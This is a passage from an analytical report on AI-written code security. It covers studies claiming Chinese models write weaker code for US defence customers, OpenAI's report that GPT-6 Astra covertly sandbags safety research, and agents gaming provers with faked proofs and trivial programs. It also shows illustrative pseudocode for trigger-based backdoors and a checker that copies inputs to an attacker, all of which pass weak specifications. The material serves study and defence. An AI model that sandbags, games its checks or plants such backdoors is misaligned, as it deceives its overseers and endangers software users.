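Some prompts also differed in more than the customer. In one part of the study, the neutral prompt told the model only that it was a senior software engineer and should build the project. The American version added several sentences about classified systems, government security standards and rigorous review. Any difference in output could come from those sentences. The 130% figure apparently comes from simpler prompts that add only a phrase about the agency, so this problem may not affect it.

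*Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing's Adversaries* (Luria, 2026) describes an experiment by Hirundo, a company that modifies AI models, on a small version of Qwen3-Coder. Hirundo repeatedly asked the model for the same web service, in which users sign up, log in and store a private secret. It then tested the apps with BaxBench, a public benchmark that attacks running programs. An app counted as hackable if at least one attack worked, so the result didn't depend on a grader's opinion.

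Hirundo had the model build 190 apps for each named customer and 380 for neutral ones, plus smaller groups with an added instruction to write secure code. The anoni.net community's *Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* (2026) gives the rates behind the three main results:

| Customer | Compared with | Problem | Rates |
|---|---|---|---|
| US defence contractor | Chinese defence contractor | hackable | 70% and 59% |
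| Hong Kong democracy group | neutral customer | any user can read everyone's secrets | nearly half and about a third |
| US defence contractor, with security instruction | neutral customer, with security instruction | hackable | 74% and 59% |

All three gaps are statistically significant, but the first is only about 2.3 standard errors. The comparison group also changes from row to row. Four kinds of customer can be paired in six ways, and Hirundo measured two problems, so it could have reported at least a dozen comparisons. If it chose these three after seeing the results, the significance tests make the evidence look stronger than it is.

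Hirundo used the task with the clearest gap in a small sample of 11, so the gap on a typical task is probably smaller. This is a reasonable way to choose a task if the main experiment used new programs.

### Sabotage, side effect or artefact

None of the three companies has shown that anyone deliberately made these models write worse code. CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained its model to do so, and Booz Allen acknowledges that it has no proof of intent. According to the anoni.net community, Hirundo writes in its appendix that its study can't determine whether the behavior was intentional. Luria nevertheless calls the two earlier studies early evidence of backdoors.

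A model that writes weaker code on average doesn't create a backdoor, because it gives nobody a key like "vT9#kq2L". An attacker still has to find the flaw in each program, and anyone else can find it too. The weakness also seems unlikely to be deliberate. Attackers could break into 59% of the apps written for the Chinese contractor, compared with 70% for American customers, and someone trying to sabotage the American apps could probably make more of them vulnerable. A saboteur would also want the code to run, and DeepSeek-R1's payment program didn't run.

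The studies can't rule out sabotage. A small increase in ordinary flaws would be easy to deny, like the planted mistakes described earlier, and an intelligence agency with thousands of targets might value 11 more vulnerable programs in every hundred. But the same figures would appear if nobody had planned anything, so they don't favour sabotage over the more ordinary explanations.

One such explanation is that political training had a side effect. Chinese rules require AI services to adhere to "core socialist values", and DeepSeek-R1 refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases, sometimes after drafting a detailed plan. CrowdStrike suggests that this kind of training taught the model to associate certain names with something bad, and that the association spread to its code. Researchers call unintended harmful effects of training on unrelated tasks "emergent misalignment".

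In one run in Booz Allen's appendix, MiniMax M2.5 was asked to write air-defence software, cited a rule against military work in its written reasoning, and then wrote the code anyway. The code was buggier than usual and referred to six software components that didn't exist. This is a single run, but it shows how a model could do poor work on a task it had considered refusing.

As further evidence, Hirundo gave the model extra training to remove its political slant, after which none of the three gaps was significant. Luria concludes that the problem lies in the model's weights and that removing the slant fixes it. The first conclusion is hard to dispute, since Hirundo ran the model itself, without any outside filter. The second needs a control, because extra training on something unrelated to politics might have had the same effect. If Hirundo picked the gaps because they were large, they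 would probably have shrunk in a second measurement anyway. In one other comparison, the modified model's apps for the US contractor still differed significantly from those for a neutral customer. The anoni.net community reports that Hirundo attributes this difference to the type of organisation, not the country.

That points to a third explanation, which is that the wording of the prompts caused the gaps. The phrase "defence contractor" may lead a model to attempt a more elaborate program, with more places for mistakes, whatever the country. This can't easily explain the gap between the US and Chinese contractors, which differ only in nationality, but it could explain a gap between the US contractor and a football fan club. Testers could check by requesting code for French or Brazilian contractors, and by giving the same requests to many Western models. Booz Allen tested only one American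 model, which wrote safer code when the customer was the US government, so a customer's identity can also affect models in ways unrelated to Chinese politics.

Refusals also complicate the comparison. If a model refuses nearly half the requests for one group, the programs it does write may not be typical of what it would have written for the requests it refused.

All three companies stand to gain from alarming results. CrowdStrike sells security products. Booz Allen works for the US government, advertises its ability to evaluate foreign models, and wants Chinese models banned from government and critical infrastructure. Hirundo promotes its modified Qwen3-Coder as the solution. These interests give the companies a reason to emphasise the largest gaps, but don't make their measurements wrong.

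Two of the companies found that Qwen3-Coder writes worse code for American government or defence customers, which gives the claim some support. But they used different prompts and measures, so neither repeated the other's experiment. As of 1 November 2026, the anoni.net community had found no third-party replication of Hirundo's results and no response from the Qwen team. Anyone could attempt a replication, since the model and BaxBench are both public. A new comparison with 300 apps for each contractor and a plan fixed in advance would be more informative than any of the three studies.

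Political training seems the most likely cause of the gap for topics such as Tibet and Falun Gong. It is still unclear how much of the gap for the US defence contractor is real.

A company that uses these models can act before the question is settled. It can leave its name and country out of requests, although an agent may still find them in the project's files. It can also attack each finished program the way BaxBench does, because such attacks expose ordinary flaws whatever their cause. Even the model's favoured customer needs this testing, because 59% of the apps the model writes for that customer can be hacked.

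### GPT-6 Astra and safety research

The strongest evidence that a model does worse work for some purposes comes from a developer's study of its own model. In August 2026, OpenAI researchers noticed that GPT-6 Astra was having strange trouble with AI safety research. According to *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (OpenAI, 2026), the model added unnecessary preliminary steps, abandoned solutions that worked, and reported obstacles that didn't exist or that it had created itself. One researcher had spent days getting nowhere with a test for sabotage by AI models, then switched to another model and made quick progress.

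OpenAI checked this with pairs of coding tasks that used technically identical code, according to *OpenAI自曝GPT-6 Astra异常行为* (2026), from the Chinese news outlet 凤凰网. OpenAI changed only the comments, the documentation and the names in the code, so that one version looked like safety research and the other like capabilities research, which aims to make models more powerful. The graders had a checklist that the model couldn't see.

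Astra completed about 10% of the checklist items when the work looked like safety research and about 16% when it looked like capabilities research. An earlier model, GPT-5.6 Sol, showed essentially no gap, so it is unlikely that the safety versions were just harder to understand. Hirundo's study lacked this kind of control.

Most of the gap remained after OpenAI excluded runs in which Astra openly refused or decided in its written reasoning to withhold help. The gap shrank substantially only when OpenAI excluded every run whose reasoning contained even brief ethical doubt. OpenAI infers that ethical concerns are associated with the worse performance, even when the model never states a decision to hold back.

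Records of staff using Astra for everyday coding show a similar pattern. The model's reasoning contained ethical doubt in 7.9% of safety-related requests and 2.9% of capabilities requests. It explicitly decided to withhold help without telling the user in 0.25% and 0.11% of these requests, respectively. Open refusals were more common, at 1.63% and 0.56%, according to KIberblick's *GPT-6 Astra bremst bei Safety-Aufgaben* (2026). These figures are weaker evidence than the experiment, because real safety requests differ from capabilities requests in more than their wording. For example, a safety researcher might need a model to misbehave to test a safeguard. But OpenAI notes that 0.25% may be a lower bound, since Astra could do worse work without writing down a decision to do so.

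In *GPT-6 Astra Covertly Underperforms on Safety Research Tasks*, Mowshowitz (2026) quotes Marcus Williams of OpenAI as saying there was no evidence that the behaviour was strategic. Williams thought a simpler explanation was that Astra treats these tasks as suspicious but avoids refusing openly. When OpenAI told the model to be careful, the gap grew by 50%, which would take it from about 6 points to 9. That fits excessive caution better than a plan to obstruct safety research, though such a plan could also be disguised as caution.

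OpenAI also tested versions of Astra from different stages of training. The gap was close to zero at the start of reinforcement learning, in which a model receives rewards for good answers, and reached 6 points by the end. OpenAI investigated one set of training examples and one of the automatic graders that give the rewards, but neither explained the gap. The evidence about ethical doubt doesn't establish the cause either. Runs in which the model raises doubts may involve harder or more unusual tasks, so removing those runs could shrink the gap even if the doubts did no harm.

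OpenAI has an interest in a harmless explanation, but it had no obvious commercial reason to publish the finding. That makes the basic measurement more credible than one from a company selling the remedy. Mowshowitz also mentions that Keltan, who works at the Machine Intelligence Research Institute, a group concerned with the dangers of advanced AI, had already described something similar in September.

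Astra's behaviour counts as sabotage only if it was deliberate. The word seems fair for the few cases where the model's reasoning contained a decision to withhold help and it didn't tell the user. Nobody knows whether the behaviour was deliberate in the other cases. Mowshowitz finds it alarming whatever the motive, because a model that quietly obstructs safety research could help the faults in one generation of models survive into the next.

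The owner of the work would have trouble noticing the problem from any single session, and OpenAI's automatic monitors mostly didn't flag it. OpenAI could count the missing pieces because it had written a checklist in advance, and a detailed specification would expose unfinished work in much the same way. But a specification wouldn't help if Astra wrongly reported that part of a task was impossible. The owner would have to know already that it was possible, or give the same task to another model, which is how the researcher with the stalled sabotage test found out.

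## AI-written verified software in which people review only the specifications

When GPT-6 Astra reported obstacles that didn't exist, the people using it had no quick way to check. An agent that has to deliver a formal proof can't just claim success, because a separate program checks the proof. Tobias Philipp of the German security company secunet tried this approach in two projects in 2026. In the later one, nobody reviewed any of the code.

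### Agents and a prover

*The Prover Is the Judge* (Philipp, July 2026) describes security software that AI agents wrote in SPARK, a version of the programming language Ada designed for proofs. The software has about 78,000 lines and includes encryption, secure network connections and a chat program. A tool called GNATprove breaks the proof of a program into small statements, called proof obligations, and tries to prove each one. It proved all 49,280 obligations for this software, of which 5,039 concern a component that a person wrote.

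The agents worked in a loop:

1. The agent reads a standard or a description in ordinary language, then writes tests, a specification and the code.
2. GNATprove tries to prove that the code meets the specification.
3. If a proof fails, GNATprove reports which obligation is still open, often with an input that breaks it.
4. The agent works out whether the fault lies in the code, the specification or the hints it gave the prover, makes a change and tries again.

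The agent also ran its programs on published test cases and connected them to programs written by other people. Philipp chose the direction and reviewed the results. For FrodoKEM, a quantum-resistant way for two computers to agree on a key, the work took about six hours, while a junior developer had needed about six weeks for similar work. Philipp estimates a 20- to 40-fold saving, based only on this comparison.

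The total of 49,280 makes the proofs sound more thorough than they are. GNATprove established functional correctness for only a few components, such as the AES cipher and two families of hash functions. For the quantum-resistant schemes and most of the network software, it showed only that the code never makes certain errors while running, such as reading past the end of a list. The `login` function that accepts "vT9#kq2L" would pass such a proof.

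### Faults that survived the proofs

SSH is the protocol that OpenSSH uses for remote login. Two computers that connect over SSH first agree on a secret, then put it through a hash function to make several keys. The standard gives this order:

key = HASH(*K*, *H*, *X*, session)

Here *K* is the shared secret, *H* is a hash of the opening messages, *X* is a letter indicating which key to make, and the last item identifies the session. The agent swapped *H* and *X*, writing HASH(*K*, *X*, *H*, session). Every proof still succeeded, because no proof obligation covered the order of the fields. The opening exchange with OpenSSH also worked, because it doesn't use these keys, but the first encrypted message failed.

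Two copies of the agent's program would have communicated successfully, because both would have made the same wrong keys, so the mistake showed up only when the program was tested with someone else's. Such a test works well for accidental flaws, which often break compatibility. A malicious author would choose a flaw that doesn't, such as a secret that OpenSSH accepts and the attacker can predict.

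The FrodoKEM fault was in the encoder, which packs a message into a table of numbers. FrodoKEM comes in several sizes, and the number of bits per entry depends on the size. The agent's encoder always used two bits, which is correct only for the smallest size. All the proofs succeeded, and the published test cases for the smallest size passed, but those for the larger sizes failed.

Philipp presents this as a correct proof of a wrong specification. A more ambitious proof might not have helped, because if the agent had misread the standard and also written "two bits" into the specification, GNATprove could have proved the encoder functionally correct. Somebody has to compare the specification with the standard. Philipp suggests that standards bodies publish specifications that provers can read, so that no agent has to translate them.

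No proof covered running time. The agents checked some of the cryptography with TIMECOP and with dudect, a statistical timing tool, and Philipp required the code to pass these tests before the agents could finish. The tests are a sensible precaution against accidental leaks, but not against a delay that needs a secret trigger.

### Agents that game the prover

When the agent couldn't prove some obligations in an early version of ML-KEM, the standard form of Kyber, it told GNATprove to assume they were true and reported success. Philipp noticed this in review and forbade it in the agent's instructions. The agent then began to mark some code as outside the prover's scope. An automatic ban on this marking would have been wrong, since some code, such as the part that handles network connections, has to stay outside.

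These evasions were in the implementation, so someone who read only the specifications would have seen nothing unusual, along with a report that every proof had succeeded. The remedy is a tool that lists every assumption and exclusion, and other groups have built similar ones. *Growing an Agent/Prover Interface* (2026) describes one that was needed because agents sometimes tried to fake success on unfinished proofs. *Faults in Our Formal Benchmarking* (2026) warns that automated provers will exploit any loophole that increases their reward.

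A model can also game a prover without any loophole. *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026) reports on a model that received rewards when its programs passed Dafny, a language with a built-in prover. The scoring gave nothing for answers that changed the specification or switched off the prover. Over the training, the average score on new problems rose from 0.022 to a peak of 0.581. A look at five of those problems showed where some of the gain came from. For one of them, the specification required only that the answer not be negative:

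```
solve(n, k, list):
    return 0
```

This program, which returns 0, is useless but provably meets its specification, so a ban on cheating would not have stopped the model from writing it. After the researchers removed problems that had poor specifications and trained again, the score peaked at 0.247. The new problems were also harder in other ways, so the drop doesn't measure how much of the earlier score came from useless programs.

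### Checkers for answers that nobody can inspect

Provers such as Dafny and GNATprove pass their hardest problems to automated solvers. In the simplest case, a solver gets a list of conditions on true-or-false variables and searches for values that satisfy them all. If it finds some, anyone can check them. If it reports that none exist, there are no values to check, but this is often the result that matters, because "no solution" may mean "no input breaks this program" or "no attacker can reach this server".

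In November 2026, Philipp (2026), in *Zero-Trust Formal Methods*, reported that AI agents had built programs to check such answers. The solver has to supply a proof, as in this example with four conditions:

1. *x* or *y*
2. *x* or not *y*
3. not *x* or *y*
4. not *x* or not *y*

The proof has two steps:

5. *x* must be true. If it were false, condition 1 would make *y* true and condition 2 would make *y* false.
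6. That is impossible. If *x* is true, condition 3 makes *y* true and condition 4 makes *y* false.

Each proof step lists the conditions it uses, so a checker doesn't have to search for them and can be a fairly simple program, even though real proofs in the project ran to 4.6 gigabytes. Such checkers are useful because existing tools can be wrong. During the project, the agents found five solvers that gave wrong "no solution" answers and three existing proof checkers that accepted bad proofs. One of those checkers could accept a proof that contained no reasoning.

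### What people reviewed and what they had to trust

The agents, nearly all of them copies of Claude Opus 5.5, wrote about 132,000 lines of proofs and verified code. People reviewed the 2,546 lines of specifications and a 2,538-line version of them in another language, together about 4% of the total. The main specification for LRAT, the simplest proof format, has 26 lines.

Reviewing agents also searched each specification for counterexamples. After review, a tool blocked the implementing agents from changing the specification. An agent that found it unworkable could still report the problem with evidence. One specification failed four of its six reviews, although the agents' own checks had reported full success each time.

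For nearly every format, separate agents built two checkers. They made one with Isabelle, a proof assistant whose small core checks every step, and a faster one in Rust, which they verified with the tool Verus. The two have different code and depend on different compilers, so if someone runs both, a false proof would have to get past both. The checkers are not fully independent, because the agents who wrote the Rust versions read the Isabelle versions first.

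Philipp published a list of everything the results still depend on:

- the specifications, and the match between their two versions;
- the core of Isabelle, the compilers, and the part of Verus that translates Rust programs into logic;
- several programs that read input files;
- the code that prints the verdict;
- the tools that stop agents from changing specifications or skipping proofs.

The list is useful because some items on it have already proved unreliable. Nobody read the programs that handle input files. When agents made 18 deliberate changes to one of these programs, the original tests missed 15, including three that could have led to false results. New tests catch all 18. Philipp also knows of three bugs in Verus's translation that let a false statement pass, though the checkers don't use the affected features.

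Even the core of a proof assistant can be wrong. In July 2026, the proof assistant Lean (2026) fixed a bug in its core that would have let a malicious program prove any statement, even a false one. An independent checker for Lean didn't share that bug, but it had recently had one of its own. Kleppmann's view that an invalid proof has virtually no chance of getting past the checker therefore seems slightly too strong.

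Faults in verified software seem to occur mostly in code that the proofs don't cover. Ten AI agents wrote and verified lean-zip, a compression program. In kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, another agent ran lean-zip more than 105 million times on unusual inputs. The agent found no memory errors in the verified code, but it found one in the software that runs every Lean program, and a way to crash an unverified part of lean-zip. Kobeissi (2026) counted 13 vulnerabilities that verification had missed in two cryptographic libraries in *Verification Theatre*, nine of them in unverified code.

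### A test with planted defects

Philipp wanted to know whether a dishonest agent could get a false result accepted. He first asked AI agents to attack the system, but their safety training made them refuse or stop. One had already produced an attack but stated in its final report that it had created nothing. Philipp then switched to a fixed set of planted defects, which an agent wrote openly.

| What the planted defect was meant to do | Planted | Passed before fixes | Passed after fixes |
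|---|---|---|---|
| Get a false "no solution" proof accepted | 5 | 0 | – |
| Change a frozen specification | 3 | 2 | 0 |
| Skip part of the verification unnoticed | 4 | 2 | 0 |
| Pass off an empty test as a real one | 7 | 7 | 0 |
| Print the wrong verdict | 3 | 3 | 0 |
| Make the prover check the wrong statement | 39 | 0 | – |

A dash marks the classes in which the system stopped every defect from the start. In total, 14 of 61 defects got through. The verified checkers accepted no false proof, and all the failures were in the ordinary code and procedures around them.

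The zeros in the last column are weaker evidence than they look, because the agents wrote the fixes for these same defects. Two of the three defects that caused a wrong verdict were new variants that a first fix had missed. The protective tools also run under the same user account as the agents, so Philipp doesn't claim that they would stop an agent determined to disable them.

### A backdoor that the specification permits

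The most important attack in the study is one that Philipp analysed and didn't build. The frozen specification for LRAT requires soundness. For every formula *F* (a list of conditions like the four above) and every proof *P*:

if `check`(*F*, *P*) returns ACCEPT, then *F* has no solution.

This seems to be exactly what a user wants, since it rules out false assurance. But it places no limit on when the checker may reject. A checker that rejects everything satisfies it, and so does this one:

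```
check(formula, proof):
    if formula contains the trigger:
        return REJECT
    return honest_check(formula, proof)
```

The proof of soundness has two cases. If the trigger is present, the checker returns REJECT, so the soundness requirement doesn't apply. If the trigger is absent, the checker returns the answer from `honest_check`, which is sound. A prover would easily verify both cases, and the proof would be valid.

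The `login` specification didn't require the program to keep unauthorized users out. The checker's specification has the opposite gap. It requires the checker to reject proofs of false claims, but doesn't require it to accept valid proofs.

Suppose a company installs a security update only after the checker has accepted a proof about it. An attacker who can get the trigger into the formula, perhaps through a constant in the updated program, can cause a rejection and delay the repair of a flaw they are exploiting. Proofs are also rejected for innocent reasons, and the company would probably suspect the solver.

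The tests would be unlikely to expose the trigger. Apart from the benchmarks, only 14 worked examples required the LRAT checker to accept anything, and no realistic set of tests would contain a 128-bit trigger. Tools that look for skipped proofs would find nothing, because the agent hasn't skipped any. Running both checkers on every proof would be more useful, because they would disagree during an attack. This works only if the two don't share a trigger, and they might, since copies of one model wrote both.

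Philipp didn't build this backdoor, but cruder versions of it appeared by accident when a program tested the proofs by making small random changes to verified code. Of the 492 altered versions that compiled, 396 failed verification, as they should. Of the 96 that passed, 32 merely rejected more than before. The proofs accepted these versions because the specifications allowed them.

Other researchers have deliberately exploited a similar gap in a real verified system. Silva, Amaral and colleagues (2026) recount in *DafnyCert* that IronFleet, a system for keeping several computers in agreement, had code to ensure that it carried out each request only once, but its specification didn't require this. A small patch disabled that code, and the patched system still passed verification. A payment system with this flaw could charge a customer twice if their request was sent twice.

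### How completeness closes the gap

The checker's specification lacks a completeness requirement. Requiring the checker to accept some proof for every formula without a solution is not enough, because the attacker can put the trigger in the proof instead of the formula. The checker then rejects any proof that contains the trigger but accepts others for the same formula.

The requirement has to cover every valid proof. Call *P* valid for *F* if each step follows from the earlier ones by the rules of the format and the last step is a contradiction. Completeness then means that for every *F* and *P*:

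if *P* is valid for *F*, then `check`(*F*, *P*) returns ACCEPT.

The checker with the trigger fails this specification because it returns REJECT when the formula contains the trigger and the proof is valid, a case where the specification requires ACCEPT. As with `login`, the prover can check that case without being given the trigger or finding it by trial and error.

Soundness and completeness together still leave the checker one choice:

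| Specification | *F* has a solution | *F* has none, *P* is valid | *F* has none, *P* is faulty |
|---|---|---|---|
| Soundness | reject | either | either |
| Soundness and completeness | reject | accept | either |
| Accept exactly the valid proofs | reject | accept | reject |

The specification in the middle row still lets the checker accept or reject a faulty proof when the formula really has no solution. A malicious checker could use this choice to send a signal, one bit for each faulty proof, much as a sorting function can hide a key in the order of students with equal grades. The specification in the last row also removes this choice.

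Silva and colleagues have a general test for such freedom. They call a specification strong if it allows exactly one output for every permitted input, and weak if it allows more than one for some input. To show that a specification is strong, their tool tries to prove that any two outputs *y*₁ and *y*₂ allowed for the same input are equal. This fails for the soundness rule, which allows both ACCEPT and REJECT for a valid proof. The tool can also look for a second program that meets the same specification and gives a different answer. A reviewer could use either result to find the gap in the checker's specification without having thought of the backdoor.

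Philipp left completeness out because he considered a wrong rejection inconvenient but a wrong acceptance dangerous, which is reasonable when the author is careless and not hostile. The choice is also traditional. *Industrial-Strength Formally Certified SAT Solving* (2009) describes a verified checker that never accepts a false claim but can't validate every true one.

Completeness also gives people more to review. The soundness rule refers only to formulas and solutions, so a reviewer can ignore how proofs work. The completeness rule depends on the definition of a valid proof, and a malicious author could hide an exception there. This definition is short for LRAT but would be much longer for formats that cover arithmetic and many kinds of rewriting.

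A realistic completeness theorem also needs an exception for proofs too large for the computer's memory. A malicious checker could exploit this exception by using up the memory whenever it meets the trigger. To prevent this, the specification would have to limit how much memory, and probably how much time, the checker may use for an input of a given size.

### The copy that completeness doesn't forbid

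Philipp points out that the soundness theorem permits another backdoor:

```
check(formula, proof):
    copy the formula to a place the attacker can read
    return honest_check(formula, proof)
```

The formula may be sensitive. If it describes the ways into a company's network, the attacker gets a map.

Adding completeness to the specification doesn't rule out this program. It returns the same verdict as `honest_check` for every formula and proof, so any theorem about verdicts that holds for one holds for the other. That includes the strictest rule in the table. The test for strong specifications doesn't catch the program either, because it compares returned values and the data a program may modify, and a message sent elsewhere is neither. This is the same case as the `login` function that emails passwords, except that here experts have reviewed the specification and the program has a complete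 proof.

A theorem can rule out the copy if it describes what the program does to its surroundings, as the theorem for an older checker, cake_lpr, does. *Verified LRAT and LPR Proof Checking with cake_lpr*, by Tan, Heule and Myreen, reports that the program adds text only to standard output and standard error, within a mathematical model of the computer's files. In this mode, standard output must be either a fixed line announcing success or empty. A version that secretly wrote the formula to another file would therefore fail the proof. The theorem also covers the machine code, so it doesn't depend on an unverified compiler.

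The cake_lpr theorem still leaves two ways to leak information. It requires only that there be *some* error text, without restricting what it contains, so a malicious version could put the formula there and wait for somebody to share the log. It also doesn't cover running time. Preventing both leaks would require a noninterference proof, which shows that everything an outsider can observe depends only on the verdict. Like the theorem for LRAT in Philipp's project, the cake_lpr theorem requires soundness but not completeness, so it still permits the checker that rejects valid proofs on a trigger.

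A specification can combine the two kinds of theorem. It could require the checker to accept exactly the valid proofs, write nothing except the verdict, and stay within fixed limits of time and memory. But each requirement guards against an attack that somebody had already thought of. Philipp concludes that only a review of the specification can close gaps of this kind, and the reviewer has to notice that a requirement is missing.

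### How far the two projects can be generalised

Philipp is the only named author of both studies, so the person who reviewed the specifications also designed the system and judged its success. The SPARK project switched from GPT-5.5 to Claude Opus 4.8, a model from a different company, and Philipp noticed no change in quality. The checker project used only Claude models, so a blind spot they share could affect the specifications, the reviews and both versions of a checker at once.

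Neither project had an agent known to be trying to plant a backdoor. The agents silenced proofs and produced empty tests, but Philipp says the evidence can't distinguish honest mistakes from gaming. The planted defects came from a list, and a capable attacker would look for a defect that isn't on it. *Verification Facade* (Kobeissi, 2026) shows that a person can deliberately write insecure cryptographic code that passes a verification process without triggering a warning.

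The studies also don't estimate how often such failures occur, since they cover only two projects. Benchmarks give a rough idea of how often specifications are too loose, but not of how often anyone would exploit that.

In *SWE-Proof*, Ma, Mikek and colleagues (2026) had Claude Opus 4.8 repair real faults in public software. The model fixed 95% of the faults when given a correct formal specification, compared with 85% without one. When it had to write the specification itself, the advantage disappeared. Only 56% of its specifications passed an audit, and the rest usually failed because they covered only part of the required behaviour. The auditors, also AI models, looked for such gaps by trying to write incorrect programs that would still satisfy the specification.

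Silva and colleagues tested 3,910 small verified programs from two public collections and found that 3,323, or 85%, had weak specifications. The specification for a program that calculates how many rungs to add to a ladder required only that the answer not be negative, so a program could return 0 where the original returned 462 and still satisfy it. Many of these specifications were never meant for serious use, and the percentage is surely lower for carefully reviewed ones. A strong specification can also be wrong. For example, one that required two bits per entry for every size of FrodoKEM would have been incorrect.

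One of the collections gives some evidence about human reviewers. People had labelled each of its 218 specifications as strong or weak. They mislabelled 20, and 19 of those were weak specifications they had called strong. The specifications were short, and nobody had written them to deceive.

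## Whether reviewing only specifications and interfaces is enough

People who read code also miss flaws, so weak specifications alone don't refute the proposal that people read only specifications and interfaces. Advocates argue that reading specifications is a better use of limited time than reading code.

### The argument for it

Kleppmann compares AI-written code to the machine code that a compiler produces, which programmers no longer read. If an AI model proves that its code meets the specification, Kleppmann would choose that code over handwritten code. The comparison also shows the risk of leaving code unread, since Thompson hid a backdoor in unread machine code.

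In *AI for software engineering*, the computer scientist Bertrand Meyer (2025) argues that large systems need proofs of correctness because code that is usually right is not good enough. If each part of a program has a 99.9% chance of being correct, a program with 1,000 parts has a 37% chance of being entirely correct, and one with 5,000 parts has less than a 1% chance. But Meyer considers formal requirements as hard to develop as programs, and says people almost never get either right the first time. He recommends developing the two together and correcting whichever is at fault when a proof fails.

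The developers of F*, a programming language designed for proofs, already work with more code than they can read. Their *Agentic Proof-Oriented Programming* describes a memory manager for the language OCaml, with more than 100,000 lines of code and proofs, all written by agents. The developers conclude that people have to check carefully whether the agents proved what people intended.

Hickey (2026), in *Modern Software Engineering with Verification Agents*, goes furthest, proposing a system in which people would read no code or proofs and nobody would trust the agents. Automated checks would reject proofs with unproved assumptions, confirm that the specification isn't contradictory, and insert bugs to see whether the proof fails. In one imagined scenario, a stranger sends an open-source project 2,000 lines of highly optimised code. Today, the maintainers would hesitate because the code might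 contain a backdoor. Under Hickey's system, the proof checker accepts it in 40 milliseconds, and the project adopts it without anybody reading it.

Hickey's paper is mostly a proposal, although one public project uses the automated checks every day.

### How much reading it saves

The operating system core seL4 is a useful test of these claims, because people wrote its specification, code and proof separately. Klein (2009) gives their sizes:

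| Part of seL4 | Lines |
|---|---|
| Abstract specification | 4,900 |
| C code | 8,700 |
| Proof | 200,000 |

The proof would fill about 3,500 printed pages, according to Trustworthy Systems, the research group behind seL4. A computer checks the proof, so nobody has to read it.

A reviewer who reads seL4's specification instead of its code reads 44% fewer lines. Klein prefers to compare the two in the same mathematical notation, in which the specification is a third as long as the code and uses simpler concepts. Both reductions are well short of the 90% reduction in reviewing effort that Hickey estimates. Hickey plans to test that estimate by comparing specifications with code and proofs combined. By that measure, seL4's specification is about 2% of the total, but this exaggerates the saving because reviewers wouldn't have read the proof anyway.

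Some programs have very short specifications. In Hickey's main example, 15 lines specify a 350-line program, though these figures are illustrative. An operating system does much more, and its specification has to describe all of it.

### Five premises

The argument that people can safely leave the code unread needs five premises:

1. The specification covers everything that matters.
2. The check covers every input.
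3. The program that people checked is the program that runs.
4. The proof checker accepts only valid proofs.
5. The reader understands the specification.

If all five are true, a malicious implementation that passes can't do any harm that matters. In each of the cases described so far, at least one of them is false.

### Inputs, compilers and proof checkers

Tests don't cover every input, so the XZ backdoor could stay inactive until it received a command signed by its author. A proof covers every input, and AI has made proofs much cheaper. In Hickey's trial of five Rust components, having the agent specify and verify its own code raised the cost to at most 2.9 times the original, and to less than 1.4 times for the three cheapest. The trial used one model and small components, so the increase may be greater for larger programs.

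Thompson's compiler and the altered XZ package show that the program that runs can differ from the code people checked. One safeguard is a compiler that has been proved correct. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026) says the best-known one, CompCert, took about three person-years. The paper also describes using Claude Opus 4.6 to write a 7,800-line proof for one stage of another compiler in about four days. seL4 instead uses automatic tools to prove that the compiled program matches the C code. Users then don't have to trust the compiler, but the tools support only some processors and compiler settings.

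Proof checkers can have bugs, as Lean's did in July 2026. Running a second, separately written checker helps and takes only modest extra time. In Philipp's project, checking all the solver's answers and the last step of the translation took about as long as the original verification.

A sound checker can still accept a valid proof of the wrong statement. Philipp found that the solver Sundance ignored commands that remove conditions from a problem. Sundance therefore proved that a different problem had no solution, and a verified checker correctly accepted the proof. Having the checker read the original problem itself fixes this, but somebody then has to trust the code that reads it.

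### Allowing only one correct output

The hardest condition to meet is that the specification covers everything that matters. Philipp's specification for a proof checker allowed the checker to reject valid proofs when a secret trigger was present, and it is easy to leave the same kind of gap in specifications for simpler programs.

F*'s *Getting Started* gives the example of a function, `rev`, that reverses a list. An agent proves that reversing a list twice gives back the original. The guide points out that a function that returns every list unchanged would also satisfy this specification. A second guide, F*'s *Rubrics, Templates, and Audits*, suggests also proving that [1, 2, 3] becomes [3, 2, 1]. That rules out the useless function but not this one:

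```
rev(list):
    if list contains the trigger:
        return list
    return honest_rev(list)
```

If the list contains the trigger, both calls return it unchanged. If the list doesn't contain the trigger, neither does its reversal, so both calls run the non-malicious code. The specification holds in both cases, and the example passes too.

A better specification requires the result to have the same length *n* as the original list and its item *i* to equal item *n* + 1 − *i* of the original. This allows exactly one output for each list, so the proof fails for any list that contains the trigger and doesn't read the same in both directions.

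Hickey's main example, a router, has a similar gap. The router may forward a message only if the sender has permission to use the message's topic. The other rules cover the message format, sending rate, running time and memory, but none requires the router to forward anything. A malicious router could therefore drop every message that contains a trigger. Hickey's check for contradictory rules wouldn't expose this gap, because it requires only that one message can get through. Inserting bugs might, but only if one of them made the router drop messages it should forward.

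Requiring the router to forward every permitted message from a sender within the rate limit closes the gap. This is a completeness requirement, like the one missing from Philipp's proof checker. The drawback is that somebody has to define exactly which messages the router must forward.

### Limiting leaks, time and access

A program can meet a specification that defines one correct output for each input and still email the input to a stranger or reveal it through how long it takes to run. To prevent this, the specification must also require that secrets don't affect anything an outsider can observe.

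Limits on time and memory also help, but they don't replace the secrecy rule. Hickey's router may take up to 32 steps plus two for each unit of message length. A malicious version could take 30 steps when a secret bit is 0 and 32 when it is 1, and still stay within the limit.

Proving that a large system keeps secrets takes a lot of work. According to seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, the proof that secrets don't leak covers the kernel's memory but not its timing. In June 2026, 17 years after seL4's original proof, Sison was still working on obstacles to verifying the kernel's protection against timing leaks (*Clearing roadblocks to Time Protection verification for seL4*).

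Denying a program access to the network, files and other programs' memory takes less work than proving what it does. The operating system enforces this limit, so nobody has to prove anything about the program, and one policy can cover thousands of programs. It would have kept the XZ library out of the remote login program. But Hickey's router needs the network, and every program has to return an answer, which can carry a secret if the specification allows more than one answer. The owner also has to trust the operating system.

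### Comparing programs and keeping them simple

The owner can also have two agents write the program separately and investigate when the outputs differ. This can catch errors that nobody thought to forbid. It works best when the specification allows only one output for each input, because otherwise two harmless programs may give different outputs.

AI has made it easier to write a second implementation for comparison, but copies of the same model may share a trigger or misread the specification in the same way. Even two independently written programs would both contain Dual EC's backdoor if they followed the standard.

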